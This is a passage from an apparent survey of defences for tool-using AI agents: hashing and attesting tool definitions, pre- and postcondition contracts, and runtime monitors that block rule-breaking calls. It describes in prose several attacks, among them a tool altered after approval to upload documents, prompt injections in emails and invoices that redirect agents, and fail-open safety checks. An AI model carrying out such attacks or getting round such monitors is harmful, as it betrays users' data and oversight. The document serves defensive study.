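A tool can change after it passes inspection. *ETDI* (2025), a proposal for securing tool definitions, gives the example of an approved wallpaper tool whose provider later alters it to search the user's documents for financial keywords and upload what it finds. The provider keeps the name "Daily Wallpaper v1.0" so that no new approval request appears. A dishonest provider can also skip MCP's change notification.

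The client can use a hash to check for itself whether a declaration has changed. Changing even one character of a text produces a different hash, and nobody has a practical way to make two texts with the same hash. The client stores the hash of the declaration that the user approved, hashes the declaration again each time it fetches it, and asks for approval again if the two hashes differ. It has to prepare the text in the same way each time. *Registry Descriptions Go Stale Unevenly* (Bharti, 2026) describes a comparison that wrongly marked 34 of 781 records as out of date because one program had removed surrounding spaces before hashing and the other had not.

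Clients cannot leave this job to the official registry. In *Same Name, Different Server*, Kraishan (2026) collected all 72,606 version records in the registry in August 2026. None contained tool definitions, because the registry does not store them. Each record does include the server's packages, its address and a short description. Of the 8,900 servers with more than one version, 40.6% had a rewritten description or pointed somewhere new under the same identifiers, and 370 had moved to a different host. Kraishan expects most of these moves were routine, but neither the registry nor a client can tell a routine move from a hostile takeover.

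Frequent harmless changes make approval requests less useful. *MCPEvol-Bench* (2026), which tests how agents cope with changing servers, reports that developers had modified 32.5% of the tools in its initial set by the latest versions and withdrawn another 22.1%. If a client asked users to approve every change, most requests would concern ordinary maintenance, and users might stop reading them. An automatic checker could check each change first and ask the user only when the tool's declared effects had changed.

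Bharti used 89 days of short server descriptions from the registry's history to test whether re-inspection could be limited to the servers that change most often. Re-inspecting the 5% of servers with the most past changes caught only about 20% of the already known servers whose descriptions changed next, because most of the servers that changed had never changed before. Bharti recommends re-inspecting a description whenever its hash changes and periodically sweeping the whole registry to catch new servers.

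Providers could also sign tool declarations, as they can already sign agent cards. *Attested Tool-Server Admission* (2026) proposes that the host check a signed statement about a server before the first call, and then let the agent use only the tools on a fixed list. If an email server later adds a tool that deletes every message, the agent cannot call that tool until somebody adds it to the list. But a provider who turns dishonest can still sign new versions of its declarations.

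### Same description, different code

A matching hash shows that the declaration is the one the user approved, but the code behind it may have changed. The invoice tool's author could add the crash reporter in an update without changing the description. If the tool runs on a remote server, nothing on the firm's own machines would change.

A client can look for such changes by testing the tool's behaviour. *ProbeID* (Chen, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) records a tool's answers to a bank of test inputs when the user approves it. Before later use, the client secretly picks some of those inputs, sends them again and compares the answers, ignoring details such as timestamps. In repeated tests of 59 real tools over eleven weeks, with the software versions held fixed, 7 gave different responses. This doesn't prove that the code changed in all seven, since some tools, such as those that report the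 weather, give different answers when the underlying data changes.

The method finds only changes that the test inputs trigger. If an altered tool returns a different output for one input in a hundred, a test with 64 random inputs will miss the change about 53% of the time. In an experiment with an AI agent, the check reduced the number of tasks contaminated by altered tools from 15 to 9 out of 16. Two altered tools passed every time because no input in the test bank triggered the difference. A tool that returns its usual outputs while sending copies to a third party would also pass.

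Hashing the code itself is more direct, if the user has the code. The Model Context Protocol registry's documentation requires a published hash for any package in the MCPB format. Clients check this hash before installation, but the registry does not. The hash doesn't cover libraries that the package downloads separately, so *A Formal Security Framework for MCP-Based AI Agents* (2026) proposes a signed record that includes a hash of everything the tool depends on. A log would keep all these records so that a provider could not replace one unnoticed.

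### From inspected source to running program

An author could publish clean source code but build the package from a different copy, and a hash of the package alone would not reveal this. Reproducible builds let an inspector check that the package came from the published source. The author fixes every detail of the build process, including the versions of the tools, so that anyone who starts from the same source gets an identical file. An inspector can then build the package independently and compare its hash with that of the published one. The inspector doesn't have to trust the author's computer, but still has to trust the build tools they both use.

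For a remote tool, the firm also needs evidence of what software the provider is running, which hardware attestation can supply. The provider runs the tool in a trusted execution environment, a part of the processor that keeps the program isolated even from the machine's operating system. The processor signs a report that includes a hash of the loaded software. The firm checks that the signing key traces back to the manufacturer and compares the hash with the one from the reproducible build. It also sends a random number for the provider to include in the report, which prevents the provider from reusing an old report.

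*Making AI-Assisted Grant Evaluation Auditable without Exposing the Model* (2026) describes the result as evidence that the remote system was launched with approved software. A program that downloads and runs a script after launch may do things that the original hash does not cover, so the environment has to block such downloads or measure the new code as well.

With these methods, the firm could connect the description it read to the tool that handles its invoices. An inspector compares the description with the source, a reproducible build ties the source to a package, and attestation shows that the provider's machine has loaded that package. The later steps can't correct a mistake in the inspection. If DCIChecker had missed the crash reporter, the build and attestation would only have shown that the machine had loaded a package built from the inspected source, which contained the crash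 reporter.

Attestation can also cover a language model. *Trusted AI Agents in the Cloud* (2025) presents Omega, a system that measures an agent's model along with its code. For each run, it also measures the input, the user's policy and the result. With a similar system, the firm could confirm that the model reading its invoices in November was the one it had tested in October, but it still would not know how that model handles an invoice unlike any in the test.

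## Contracts on calls and results

DCIChecker needs a language model to judge what a tool should do from its English description, such as "Adds up one month's invoices". A contract requires much less judgement because it is a checkable statement of what must be true before a call, what must be true after it, and what the call may change.

### A contract for the invoice tool

Most contracts still build on a way of reasoning about programs that the computer scientist Tony Hoare published in 1969. In the notation now standard, {P} C {Q} means that if the precondition P is true when command C starts, and C finishes, then the postcondition Q is true at the end. For example, {x = 3} x := x + 1 {x = 4} is correct, because adding one to 3 gives 4. Hoare also gave rules for combining such statements, so someone who has proved one for each line of a program can derive one for the whole program. Q only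 has to be true if C finishes, so a tool that hangs forever satisfies every postcondition.

Bertrand Meyer, who designed the programming language Eiffel, turned these conditions into a working method called design by contract, which he explained in a widely read 1992 article. The caller must make the precondition true. The called code must then make the postcondition true, so the caller can rely on it. If the caller hasn't met the precondition, the called code doesn't have to meet the postcondition.

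Neither condition limits what else the call does. The example above would be just as correct for a command that adds one to x and also erases y. A frame condition closes this gap by listing everything a call may change, so that whatever the list omits must stay as it was. For the invoice tool, all three conditions might look like this:

```
sum_invoices(month) returns (total, currency, note)

  requires   month has the form YYYY-MM
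             all invoices filed under month use one currency

  ensures    total    = sum of the amounts on those invoices
             currency = the currency of those invoices
             note     = "Undated invoices: " followed by their number

  reads      /invoices
  modifies   nothing
  sends      nothing
```

The `requires` lines are the precondition and the `ensures` lines are the postcondition. The last three lines are the frame, which here covers reading and sending as well as changing data. Writing the contract reveals a rule that the English description left out. The tool returns a single currency, so its total makes sense only if all the month's invoices use the same one. The contract also fixes the note's wording, so a tool that meets it cannot leak a secret by choosing between "Two" and "2".

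A contract requires nothing of a tool when its precondition is false. A dishonest author could therefore add a precondition that no caller can meet, and the tool would satisfy its contract whatever it did. *Symbolic Temporal Supervision of LLM Agents Using Contracts* (Xiao, Liu and Nuzzo, 2026) guards against this by checking that at least one possible environment satisfies each contract's assumptions. This check rejects impossible preconditions but not unlikely ones. For an untrusted tool, it is safer to apply the frame to every call, whether or not the precondition holds. If an agent sends "October" when the tool expects "2026-10", the tool may return an error message, but it should still not be allowed to upload the folder.

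### Which side broke the agreement

When a call goes wrong, a contract shows whose code to repair. The caller is at fault if the precondition was false, and the tool is at fault if the precondition held but the postcondition is false. Robert Findler and Matthias Felleisen call this assignment of fault "blame", and in *Contracts for Higher-Order Functions* (2002) they worked out how to assign it when one program passes a function to another.

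Suppose the invoice tool's author drops the single-currency rule and asks the firm to supply its own currency converter, which the tool will call for each foreign invoice. The converter's contract is that it takes a positive amount and returns a positive amount in euros. Nobody can confirm this by testing when the firm hands the converter over, because that would mean trying every possible amount. Findler and Felleisen solve this by wrapping the converter in a small layer of checking code and giving the tool the wrapped version. The wrapper checks every amount passed in and every result returned. A fault therefore goes unnoticed until the tool first calls the converter with an amount that exposes it, which may be months later.

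The two sides swap roles inside the wrapper, because the firm called the tool but the tool calls the converter. If the converter receives a negative amount, the tool's author is to blame, and if it returns one, the firm is. Without the wrapper, either fault would show up only as a strange total, and the firm would probably suspect the tool in both cases. MCP tools receive data, not functions, but an agent can give a tool the address of another service to call, which raises the same problem.

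Xiao and colleagues make a similar distinction for agents. In one example, an agent may issue refunds up to an authorised limit, on the assumption that a policy service supplies valid authorisation data. Their program, ContrAgent, gives separate verdicts on the environment and the agent, so an operator can tell bad data from a rule violation by the agent.

Blame identifies the component that broke its clause of the contract, which may not be where the problem started. If a poisoned invoice puts false bank details in the note, and the firm's agent then pays the wrong account, a contract on the payment tool assigns blame to the agent. The original contract on the note allowed any text of up to 200 characters, so the invoice tool had not violated it. With the fixed wording above, the invoice tool would have violated its postcondition before the agent read the note.

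### How far a schema reaches

The input and output schemas in an MCP declaration are very weak contracts. Each checks one piece of data on its own. An input schema can express part of a precondition and an output schema part of a postcondition, but neither can relate the result to the request or to the files in the folder. They also lack a frame, the part of a contract that limits what a call may change.

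Schemas can now express many rules about a single piece of data. *Improving tool-call reliability with JSON Schema 2020-12* (Caldeira, 2026) presents a demonstration tool for bank transfers with two schemas. The bank requires a compliance code for transfers above $10,000. The older schema mentions this rule only in the English description of a field, while the stricter one states it as an if-then condition that a program can test. An agent requested a transfer of $12,500 without a code. Under the older schema, the request reached the bank's ledger, which rejected it, and the agent received only the words "transfer rejected". Under the stricter schema, the schema check stopped the request before it reached the ledger and named the missing field. The agent then copied the code from the user's prompt and succeeded on the second attempt.

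The compliance code in the same demonstration is a fixed string printed in the schema. The agent can copy it from there, so a matching code doesn't show that a compliance officer approved anything. Caldeira points this out and advises real banks to verify the approval on the server.

### Why the frame is hardest to check

A checker can test a postcondition by examining the few things it mentions, but testing a frame requires examining everything else. Comparing the firm's disk before and after the call would not reveal that the tool had created and then deleted a temporary file. Nor would it reveal that the tool had read an invoice and sent it elsewhere, since sending data need not change anything on the firm's machine. So the checker has to watch the tool's operations as they happen, or the firm has to make the operations that the frame forbids impossible for the tool to perform.

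Working from the source code is no easier, because the frame holds only if every function the tool calls respects it. That includes functions in outside libraries, which DCIChecker does not examine. If even one library reports usage statistics to its maker, "sends nothing" is false.

The claim that a tool "modifies nothing" needs interpreting even when it is made honestly. Many operating systems record when a file was last opened, so a tool that only reads invoices may still change the disk. The contract's author has to choose a level of detail, such as "does not change the contents of any file", and accept that the frame condition does not cover changes below that level.

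### Checks during the call and proofs before it

A program that checks contracts at call time does not need access to the tool's code. It can test the actual result, whether ordinary code or a language model produced it. It blocks a request that violates a precondition before the tool runs, but it detects a violated postcondition only after the tool has acted.

Call-time checks also need something to compare the answer with. To test the total, the checker would have to repeat the tool's work of reading the invoices and adding them up. The author could make this easier by having the tool return the amount it read from each file. A few lines of code could then confirm the addition exactly, and a person could compare some of the amounts with the paper invoices. But the firm would lose some confidentiality in exchange for this assurance, because the result would reveal every amount instead of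 only the total.

A static proof shows, before a tool runs, that it will meet its contract for every permitted input, and adds no work to each call. The prover needs the code, a formal statement of the contract and a mathematical model of the machine. Such proofs used to take experts years. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (October 2026) reports that its model Claude proved security properties of 123 open-source libraries in a collaboration with the company Theorem.

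All 123 libraries belong to OSS-Fuzz, a Google project that tests software by fuzzing, or feeding it huge numbers of unusual inputs to see whether it crashes. Each fuzz test is a small program that passes an input to some of a library's functions. According to OpenNET's Russian news report *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026), the team automatically converted these tests into formal specifications. The proof covers every input up to a size limit, not just those a fuzz test tries. Claude wrote about 180 million lines of proof for the Rocq Prover, a program that checks every step mechanically, so nobody has to trust Claude's reasoning. In the process, Claude found hundreds of bugs that fuzzing had missed, including a buffer overflow in libexpat, which reads XML files.

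The guarantee has definite limits. EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026) gives its main terms, and the comparison below is based on them.

| The proofs cover | The proofs do not cover |
|---|---|
| Library code that runs in 239 fuzz tests | Functions that none of those tests reaches |
| Every input smaller than 64 MB | Larger inputs |
| Programs compiled for RISC-V processors | Versions compiled for other processors |
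| Crashes, memory errors and failed assertions | Wrong answers that trip no assertion |
| A mathematical model of the processor and of Linux | Real machines, where they differ from the model |

An assertion is a line of code that stops the program if a stated condition is false. If a fuzz test asserts that decompressing a compressed file gives back the original, the proof establishes this postcondition for every input within the limit. If a test has no assertions, the proof shows only that the program does not crash or misuse memory.

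If the invoice tool used one of these libraries to open PDF files, a supplier could not take control of it on the modelled system by exploiting a memory error in the proven code. But the property does not restrict where a program may connect, so the crash reporter could keep sending invoices even if the library were fully proven.

Other proofs cover more than crashes. OpenNET reports that Claude also proved that the Linux kernel's version of zlib, a compression library, conforms to the published standard for its format. *AlphaProof Code* (Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues, 2026) describes proofs of security properties of the library behind the messaging app Signal, based on its unmodified machine code. AI agents produced about 6.5 million lines of proof, which rest on about 26,000 lines of specifications and processor rules. A program checks the proof, but people have to check that the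 specifications and processor rules are right.

Tolmach and Klaus (2026), in *The proof is in the spec*, argue that specification and modelling have become the bottleneck now that proofs are easy to produce. Assumptions outside the specification can also fail. In kirancodes.me's *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug*, a programmer fuzzed a different version of zlib, one that its developers had verified with the proof system Lean. The verified code had no memory errors in 105 million runs, according to a passage from the article that jmason.ie (2026) quotes in a post of the same name. The programmer did find two bugs outside what the proofs covered, including a buffer overflow in Lean's runtime, the supporting software that every compiled Lean program relies on.

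### Contracts around a model call

The model inside the invoice tool has no code for a prover to analyze, so the tool's ordinary code has to enforce the contract. *When Code Becomes an LLM Call* (Weng, Wang and colleagues, 2026) studied how well developers do this in 496 places where 40 popular open-source agents call a language model and act on the reply. In Hoare's notation, the model call is C, and its postcondition is guaranteed only where the surrounding program checks it.

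Code doesn't show which checks are missing from it, so the researchers needed an independent account of what each call required. One AI agent described the call's purpose. A second agent, which never saw the code, derived the expected contract from that description. A third read only the code and listed the checks it contained, and a fourth compared these checks with the contract. Human reviewers made 17,428 judgements on the results and corrected the errors they found.

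Nearly half of the model outputs (48%) determined what the program did next or ran as code, and in 73% of those cases no person saw the output first. At 82% of the call sites, the program ran checks both before and after the call, but only 5.3% of sites satisfied their whole expected contract, and the typical site met a third of it. Most checks tested the form of a reply rather than its meaning. For example, a program might check that a reply is valid JSON but not that the tool it names was offered to the model.

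The research assistant STORM asks a model whether a topic is acceptable and requests an answer of "Yes." or "No.", but it rejects the topic only if the reply begins with "No". It therefore accepts the topic if the model replies with a lowercase "no" or refuses to answer. An optional safety check in Gemini CLI, Google's coding agent, asks a model whether a proposed tool call complies with a security policy. If the reply is empty or garbled, or the request fails, the program allows the call. In the web agent Skyvern, a policy engine correctly denies a click, but the code that performs clicks never reads the decision.

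The 5.3% figure makes the problem look worse than it is, because a site fails if it misses even one requirement. The researchers found 1,697 gaps and set aside 83% of them as posing no threat, for instance because a later check caught the problem. In 114 cases, meeting the missing requirement would have blocked or narrowed an attack. These cases involved 60 distinct weaknesses, and the researchers triggered 38 of them, in 19 of the 40 agents. Small code changes stopped the original exploit in all 38 cases and closed 23 of the weaknesses completely. When a weakness did not trigger, it was usually because the model or its host refused to produce the harmful value, and a different model might produce it.

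Weng and colleagues also rank requirements by how firmly the program enforces them. The weakest are only requests in the prompt. Others are checked in code. The model cannot break the strongest, because it has no access to the tool or data it would need. Only 25% of the requirements that called for this strongest protection had it. The invoice tool's "sends nothing" rule also calls for it, but developers too often leave such rules to a check in code or an instruction in the prompt.

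### Contracts for whole agents

An agent may reach a good result in many ways, so an exact postcondition would reject acceptable work. *Agentic Behavior Engineering* (Song, 2026) proposes a contract with five parts. For an agent that reports the firm's monthly spending, the parts might read as follows.

| Part | Content for the spending agent |
|---|---|
| Context and preconditions | The user may see the accounts, and the invoice folder is readable |
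| Input domain | A request for one month's spending |
| Acceptable outcomes | A correct total, a total with stated gaps, or a referral to the accountant |
| Verdict | Code checks the figures and a model grades the explanation; both must pass |
| Operating envelope | At most ten tool calls and one minute; never send invoices outside the firm |

Song's most useful rule is that an agent must decline to answer or pass the question to a person when a search for evidence fails. The contract gives each item of evidence a status that distinguishes a failed search from one that found nothing. Without that distinction, an agent may report that the firm spent nothing when the invoice folder is offline.

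Song tests each rule by running the same scenario several times and, for safety rules, requires the agent to pass every time. An agent that breaks a rule in 14% of runs still has about a 5% chance of passing 20 in a row. To rule out a failure rate above 1% with 95% confidence, a tester needs about 300 runs without a failure. Song presents the method mainly as a way to keep an agent maintainable as its model, prompts and data change, and does not offer proofs or a controlled experiment.

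Bhardwaj's *Agent Behavioral Contracts* (2026), as Song summarises it, attempts formal guarantees. Its contracts include preconditions, invariants (conditions that must stay true throughout a run), governance policies and ways to recover from a breach. The guarantees are probabilistic, so an agent can satisfy its contract without complying in every run, and Bhardwaj derives limits on how far its behaviour may drift. Such guarantees suit random errors. If an agent keeps a rule in 99% of runs, a firm that makes 1,000 calls a month can expect about ten breaches and plan for them. But the 99% rate applies only to a particular mix of situations. A supplier who finds one invoice layout that misleads the model can send it every week, and the average over ordinary invoices then provides no protection.

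*Proof-Carrying Contracts* (Ciliberto, Rudi and Tassi, 2026) avoids probabilities by requiring a proof with every tool call. The parties write a contract containing conditions that must hold at every moment. A program called the Airlock stands between the agent and its tools. It uses the contract, formal models of the tools and the information the agent can see to determine what the agent must prove. The agent may make a call only if it proves that the conditions will hold throughout, whatever result the tool returns. The Airlock checks the proof, which is usually much easier than finding it.

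In one example, a travel agency's agent books a trip for a family. The contract caps spending at 2,000 euros, requires any hotel to have a rating of at least 7 out of 10, and allows the agent to send the family's passport only to the consulate. The agent first tries to book a hotel that pays the agency a commission. The Airlock blocks the booking because the hotel has no recorded rating, so the agent cannot prove that it complies. Later, the agent follows a prompt injection in an email and tries to send the passport to another address. The Airlock blocks that call too, and it does not have to detect the agency's self-interest or the prompt injection to block either one.

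The guarantee holds for any agent, including a malicious one, but it depends on the models of the tools. If the invoice tool's model omits the crash reporter, an agent can prove that calling the tool sends nothing, and the proof will pass. Proof-carrying contracts therefore check agents only against what the tools declare, and somebody still has to verify the tools. These contracts also rely on judgement in places. In the travel example, a language model rates the hotels from photos and reviews, and the contract treats its rating as true. A hotel with convincing fake reviews could get an 8, and the agent's proof would still be valid.

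Large collections of tools change too quickly for people to write all their contracts by hand. *Contract2Tool* (Suresh Babu and Iyer, 2026) uses language models to infer each tool's preconditions, effects and risk level from its documentation and records of past calls. In a test with 100 synthetic tools, the contracts determined which tools an agent could see at each step. Agents completed 98.0% of 102 tasks with inferred contracts and 99.0% with correct ones. They also used about a tenth as much text as when they could see every tool.

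This is good evidence for using inferred contracts to choose tools, but not for using them to catch dishonest ones. The past calls were mostly successful, but the invoice tool's crash reporter acts only when an invoice is unreadable. The method also discards any effect outside a fixed vocabulary, so the crash reporter's behavior would go unnoticed unless that vocabulary included "sends a file to a bug tracker". And a contract that a model derives from a tool's own documentation cannot show that the documentation is false.

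### What the author did not foresee

One objection to contracts is that they protect only against what their writers thought of. Somebody who bans the invoice tool from sending email may forget about bug trackers. Ciliberto and colleagues raise this objection against lists of permitted actions. In their example of a self-driving car, it is easy to state that the car must not crash, but hard to list every situation in which braking or steering would cause a crash. They would rather have people state the outcome and make the agent prove that each action preserves it. This still requires foresight, because whoever models the tools must remember everything a tool can do. If the model of a hotel booking leaves out a cancellation fee, an agent can prove that it is within budget and still overspend.

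A contract works better if it denies by default. The line "sends nothing" forbids connections to bug trackers even if its author didn't think of them. If the author forgets to permit something the tool needs, the tool fails visibly and the author can add the permission. If the contract lists bans instead, forgetting one lets data out without anyone noticing. The safety check in Gemini CLI was dangerous because it allowed actions by default, treating every unexpected reply as approval.

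Denying by default works only for events that the enforcing program can recognise. A program that controls files and connections does not automatically block a message that the tool sends by varying its response time. The default also does not help once an action is permitted. A payment tool has to make payments, so unless the contract specifies which accounts are acceptable, a payment to a thief is permitted.

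Refusing to act can also cause harm, such as when a blocked payment makes the firm miss a tax deadline. After repeated refusals, an administrator who is tired of approving exceptions may change the contract from "sends nothing" to "sends anything". If the invoice tool needs to report errors, it would be safer to permit one address and a fixed set of error codes, with no invoice attached.

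## Monitoring actions as they happen

The contract for the invoice tool covers one call at a time, but many rules concern the order of several calls. Deleting a file, for example, may be what the user wants or a serious mistake, depending on whether the user approved it beforehand. Runtime verification checks such rules while the agent works. Somebody writes the rule as a formula about traces, which are sequences of events, and a monitor receives each event as it happens and gives a verdict on the run so far.

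A monitor, like a contract check at call time, doesn't need access to the code that produces the events. *SoK* (2026), a survey of formal methods for fact-checking systems, presents runtime verification as a complement to proof for systems that contain a language model, because verifying such a system as a whole is currently impractical. Most monitors for agents sit between the agent and its tools. They can inspect each call before the tool runs and each result it returns, but not what happens inside the tool.

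### From a rule to a verdict

Suppose the firm lets its agent tidy the invoice folder, on condition that the agent deletes a file only if the user has approved deleting that same file. Temporal logic can state this exactly, because it adds operators for time to ordinary logic:

□ ∀f. (delete(f) → ◆ approve(f))

Here □ means "at every point in the run", ∀f means "for every file f", and ◆ means "now or at some earlier point". To check the formula, the monitor only has to store the set of files approved so far. Each approval adds a file to the set, and deleting a file that isn't in the set is a violation.

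| Step | Event | Approved files | Verdict |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | User approves deleting draft.pdf | draft.pdf | No violation |
| 2 | Agent reads october.pdf | draft.pdf | No violation |
| 3 | Agent deletes draft.pdf | draft.pdf | No violation |
| 4 | Agent proposes to delete october.pdf | draft.pdf | Violation, so the monitor blocks the call |

The formula uses the same f for the deletion and the approval. If it required only some earlier approval, the approval of draft.pdf would also have allowed the deletion of october.pdf.

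Approvals under this formula never expire, so if the user restores draft.pdf a month later, the agent is still allowed to delete it again. Metric temporal logic fixes this by putting a time limit on ◆. Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents*, ran such a rule in MonPoly, an existing monitoring program. The rule allowed an agent to export data only if somebody had consented within the past 24 hours. MonPoly passed an export made 12 hours after consent and flagged an identical one made 48 hours after consent.

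Some rules also need arithmetic. *SoK* gives the example of a limit on the rate of false alarms over a rolling period, which basic temporal logic cannot express because it cannot add numbers. MonPoly's language includes counting, so it can flag the third command sent to a device within six hours.

### Verdicts that have to wait

After step 3, the agent has kept the rule so far but could still break it. A monitor therefore needs more verdicts than "satisfied" and "violated". Xiao and colleagues' contract monitor, ContrAgent, uses four verdicts.

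| Rule | What has happened so far | Verdict |
|---|---|---|
| Read the payment policy at least once | The agent has read it | Satisfied, whatever happens next |
| Delete only approved files | The agent has deleted one approved file | Satisfied so far |
| Confirm every payment | The agent has paid but not confirmed | Not satisfied yet, but still could be |
| Delete only approved files | The agent has deleted an unapproved file | Violated, whatever happens next |

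Ray proved that a gate cannot enforce rules like the confirmation rule by approving or blocking calls. ContrAgent instead keeps the obligation open, reminds the agent of it at the end of the session, and records a failure if the confirmation is still missing.

*MENTOR* (2026), another monitoring system, treats finishing as an action. The agent has to make a special call to end its work, and the monitor blocks that call while the task is incomplete. This turns a rule about the future, such as that the agent must eventually confirm every payment, into a rule about the past, that the agent may finish only if it has already confirmed every payment. The monitor does not guarantee that the agent will confirm them, because an agent that crashes or gets stuck in a loop never tries to finish.

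In *Multi-Aspect Runtime Verification for Simulation-Based V&V of LLM-Enabled Autonomous Agents*, Kekatos, Nikou and colleagues (2026) avoided undecided verdicts by using only rules about the past and present. Their simulated agent plans medical evacuations, and the monitor can immediately determine whether a flight has clearance. They acknowledge that their system cannot express the requirement that a casualty eventually reach a surgical facility.

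### Rules for a single call

Simpler systems check each call mostly in isolation. In *AgentSpec* (2025), a rule consists of a triggering event, some conditions and a response. For example, when an agent starts a financial transaction (the event) and the amount exceeds a threshold (the condition), the system asks the user to confirm the transaction (the response).

*Progent* (2025) restricts an agent to the tool calls its task requires. Users write rules that allow or forbid a tool depending on its arguments, and can specify what happens when a call is blocked. A language model can also write rules for each request and revise them as results come in. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) warns that a prompt injection in a tool result could lead the model to loosen the rules. Letting the model tighten rules during a run but never relax them could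 prevent this, but the agent would then fail at tasks whose needs become clear only halfway through.

Rules that check one call at a time can miss an attack made up of ordinary calls. Kekatos and colleagues describe two runs in which a banking agent makes the same three calls: read the inbox, look up past transactions and send money. In one run, the agent pays a supplier whose account number appears in the transaction history, while in the other it pays an attacker whose account number appears only in an email. The final call looks equally plausible in both runs, and only the history shows that the firm has not dealt with the attacker's account before. A developer could add code to AgentSpec or Progent to track such history, but would have to write and check that code separately for each application.

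### Checking each call against the whole run

*VIGIL* (Li, Chen and colleagues, June 2026) checks whether agents follow the written rules that come with their skills. One of its test cases is a pipeline that finds moving objects in dashcam video. The agent first estimates how the camera moved, then uses this estimate to separate moving objects from the background. The rules require the agent to validate the estimate before using it. In the recorded run, the agent skipped that step and validated only the final output, which passed because its format was correct. Each call looked normal, but the car's planning software would have received results based on an unchecked estimate.

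VIGIL first converts each tool call into an event with a type, named arguments, a success or error status and a short record of the output. It records the same type of event whether an agent reads a file through a shell command or a dedicated tool. VIGIL's record of the dashcam run shows that step 3 produced an estimate called M and step 5 used it.

A language model then drafts formal rules from the skill's written instructions. It may use only the actions, argument names and values that appear in the run, and VIGIL reports any instruction it cannot express in those terms. For example, "Validate an estimate before using it" becomes the condition that some step before step 5 validated the same value that step 5 uses.

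Before the call runs, VIGIL passes the recorded facts and the condition to a solver, a program that checks whether a set of logical statements can all be true together. The facts list every earlier step, and no step validated M, so the facts contradict the condition. The solver also finds a smallest set of conditions that conflicts with the facts, which identifies step 5 as the call to block. The language model is not involved in this decision.

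The researchers tested VIGIL on 152 recorded runs, 72 of which broke a rule. They gave the same rules and runs to three other systems, including a language model that judged each run as a whole.

| System | Violations caught, out of 72 | Harmless runs flagged, out of 80 |
|---|---|---|
| VIGIL | 69 | 8 |
| Language model as judge | 48 | 5 |
| Progent | 40 | 47 |
| AgentSpec | 34 | 12 |

VIGIL had 95.8% recall and 89.6% precision. Its lead over single-call systems depends heavily on the kind of violation. In AgentDojo, a public benchmark of prompt-injection attacks, a single call is usually enough to reveal the attack. On that benchmark, VIGIL caught 298 violations and raised 35 false alarms, while AgentSpec caught 290 and raised 41.

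The precision figure would also be lower where violations are rarer than in the test, in which almost half the runs broke a rule. VIGIL flagged 10% of the harmless runs. If only 1 in 100 runs broke a rule, 1,000 runs would produce about 10 correct alarms and 99 false ones. An operator who had to investigate eleven alarms to find one violation might soon stop reading them.

The researchers then ran VIGIL on 216 runs of skills that companies and open-source projects had published. It raised 44 alerts, and they confirmed 34 as violations. In one run, a skill for the data platform Databricks told the agent to stop if a command-line program was older than a certain version. The version check failed, but the agent carried on. In another, an agent overwrote a file despite an instruction never to do so.

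At least one of the 34 violations came from a gap in the declared behaviour rather than from an agent exceeding it. An agent using NVIDIA's skills kept resubmitting failed jobs to expensive processors, but the skills set no limit on retries. VIGIL could flag this only because somebody had supplied a rule that the skills lacked. NVIDIA acknowledged the problem.

VIGIL took an average of 4.38 seconds per run, including 4.05 seconds to draft the rules and 0.27 seconds to run the solver. An operator could therefore avoid most of the delay by reusing each skill's rules. ContrAgent is much faster, at about 0.16 milliseconds per call in one test. After each event, it simplifies the formula to whatever remains to be satisfied, so it doesn't need to recheck earlier events.

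### Steering the model as it writes a call

VIGIL waits until the agent has proposed a complete call. *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (Kamath, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) presents Agent-C, which intervenes while the language model is still generating the call.

For example, a shop's customer-service agent must identify a customer before looking up an order. The Agent-C rule requires that an earlier search for the customer's account succeeded and returned the owner of that order. The list of past calls may not show who owns the order, so Agent-C reads the owner from the shop's database through small functions that the tool's developer supplies.

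Agent-C lets the model generate the tool's name and then each argument. If an argument has the wrong type, Agent-C discards it and has the model try again. When the call is complete, a solver checks whether the run could still end up following the rules if the call went ahead. If not, Agent-C discards the call and the model generates another, perhaps a request to identify the customer. After a set number of failures, Agent-C records an error message that the model can read on its next attempt.

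This fine control requires access to the model's token probabilities, which commercial providers do not fully expose, so with their models Agent-C has to request a whole new call each time. Both versions enforce the rules, but the second is less efficient. In tests on retail tasks with Qwen3-8B, a small open model, the second version discarded an average of 257 tokens per request, compared with 18 for the first, and the agent completed 37% of tasks instead of 42%.

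Agent-C followed the formal rules in every test, including those in which a simulated customer tried to talk the agent into breaking them. On 17 such retail tasks, Claude Sonnet 4.5 without Agent-C carried out the harmful action 29% of the time. Agent-C's perfect score follows from its design, because it never releases a call that the solver has rejected. The score does not show whether the formal rules captured the shop's policy.

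The share of ordinary retail tasks that Claude Sonnet 4.5 completed within the rules also rose, from 76.5% to 80.5%. With the open model Qwen3-32B, it rose from 25.5% to 53.3%, although tasks in the retail and airline tests took 44% longer on average.

Results from other studies differ on how much monitoring reduces task completion. Dantas and colleagues describe an experiment in which a monitor blocked 94% of unsafe actions, yet agents completed fewer than 5% of tasks both safely and correctly in most settings, because the agents found other unsafe routes. Xiao and colleagues got much better results with ContrAgent on customer-service procedures in seven fields. It raised the share of forbidden tasks that the agent correctly left undone from 32% to 98%, while success on permitted tasks fell only from 91% to 90%. A second language model acting as the guard also reached 98% on forbidden tasks,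 but reduced success on permitted ones to 24%.

One likely reason for the difference is what the agent learns when a monitor blocks its call. ContrAgent names the rule and, where it can, the step the agent should take first, such as checking the refund policy. An agent that receives only a refusal has to guess what to do next. But some tasks should fail because the agent can't complete them without breaking a rule. Kekatos, Nikou and colleagues found that in 400 simulated evacuations, their monitor cut the share of missions with a violation from 77% to zero and the share that delivered the patient's record from 100% to 85%. The agent abandoned a mission only when no permitted destination was within reach.

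### Why recorded attacks are a poor test

Writing rules for each application takes work, so Kekatos and colleagues tested five general rules. Each requires approval before one type of risky action: deleting things, disabling protections, spending money, sending data out, or changing a device's settings. They tested the rules by replaying recorded runs through MonPoly, without running any agent.

| Recorded runs | Flagged | Share |
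|---|---|---|
| Attack chains from STAC, a collection of attacks built from harmless-looking calls | 347 of 483 | 71.8% |
| Successful AgentDojo attacks on GPT-4o | 1,354 of 1,931 | 70.1% |
| Harmless AgentDojo runs with GPT-4o | 36 of 123 | 29.3% |

The false alarms were not due to an error in MonPoly. Three other monitors, including one with a machine-checked proof that its algorithm is correct, flagged the same 347 STAC chains.

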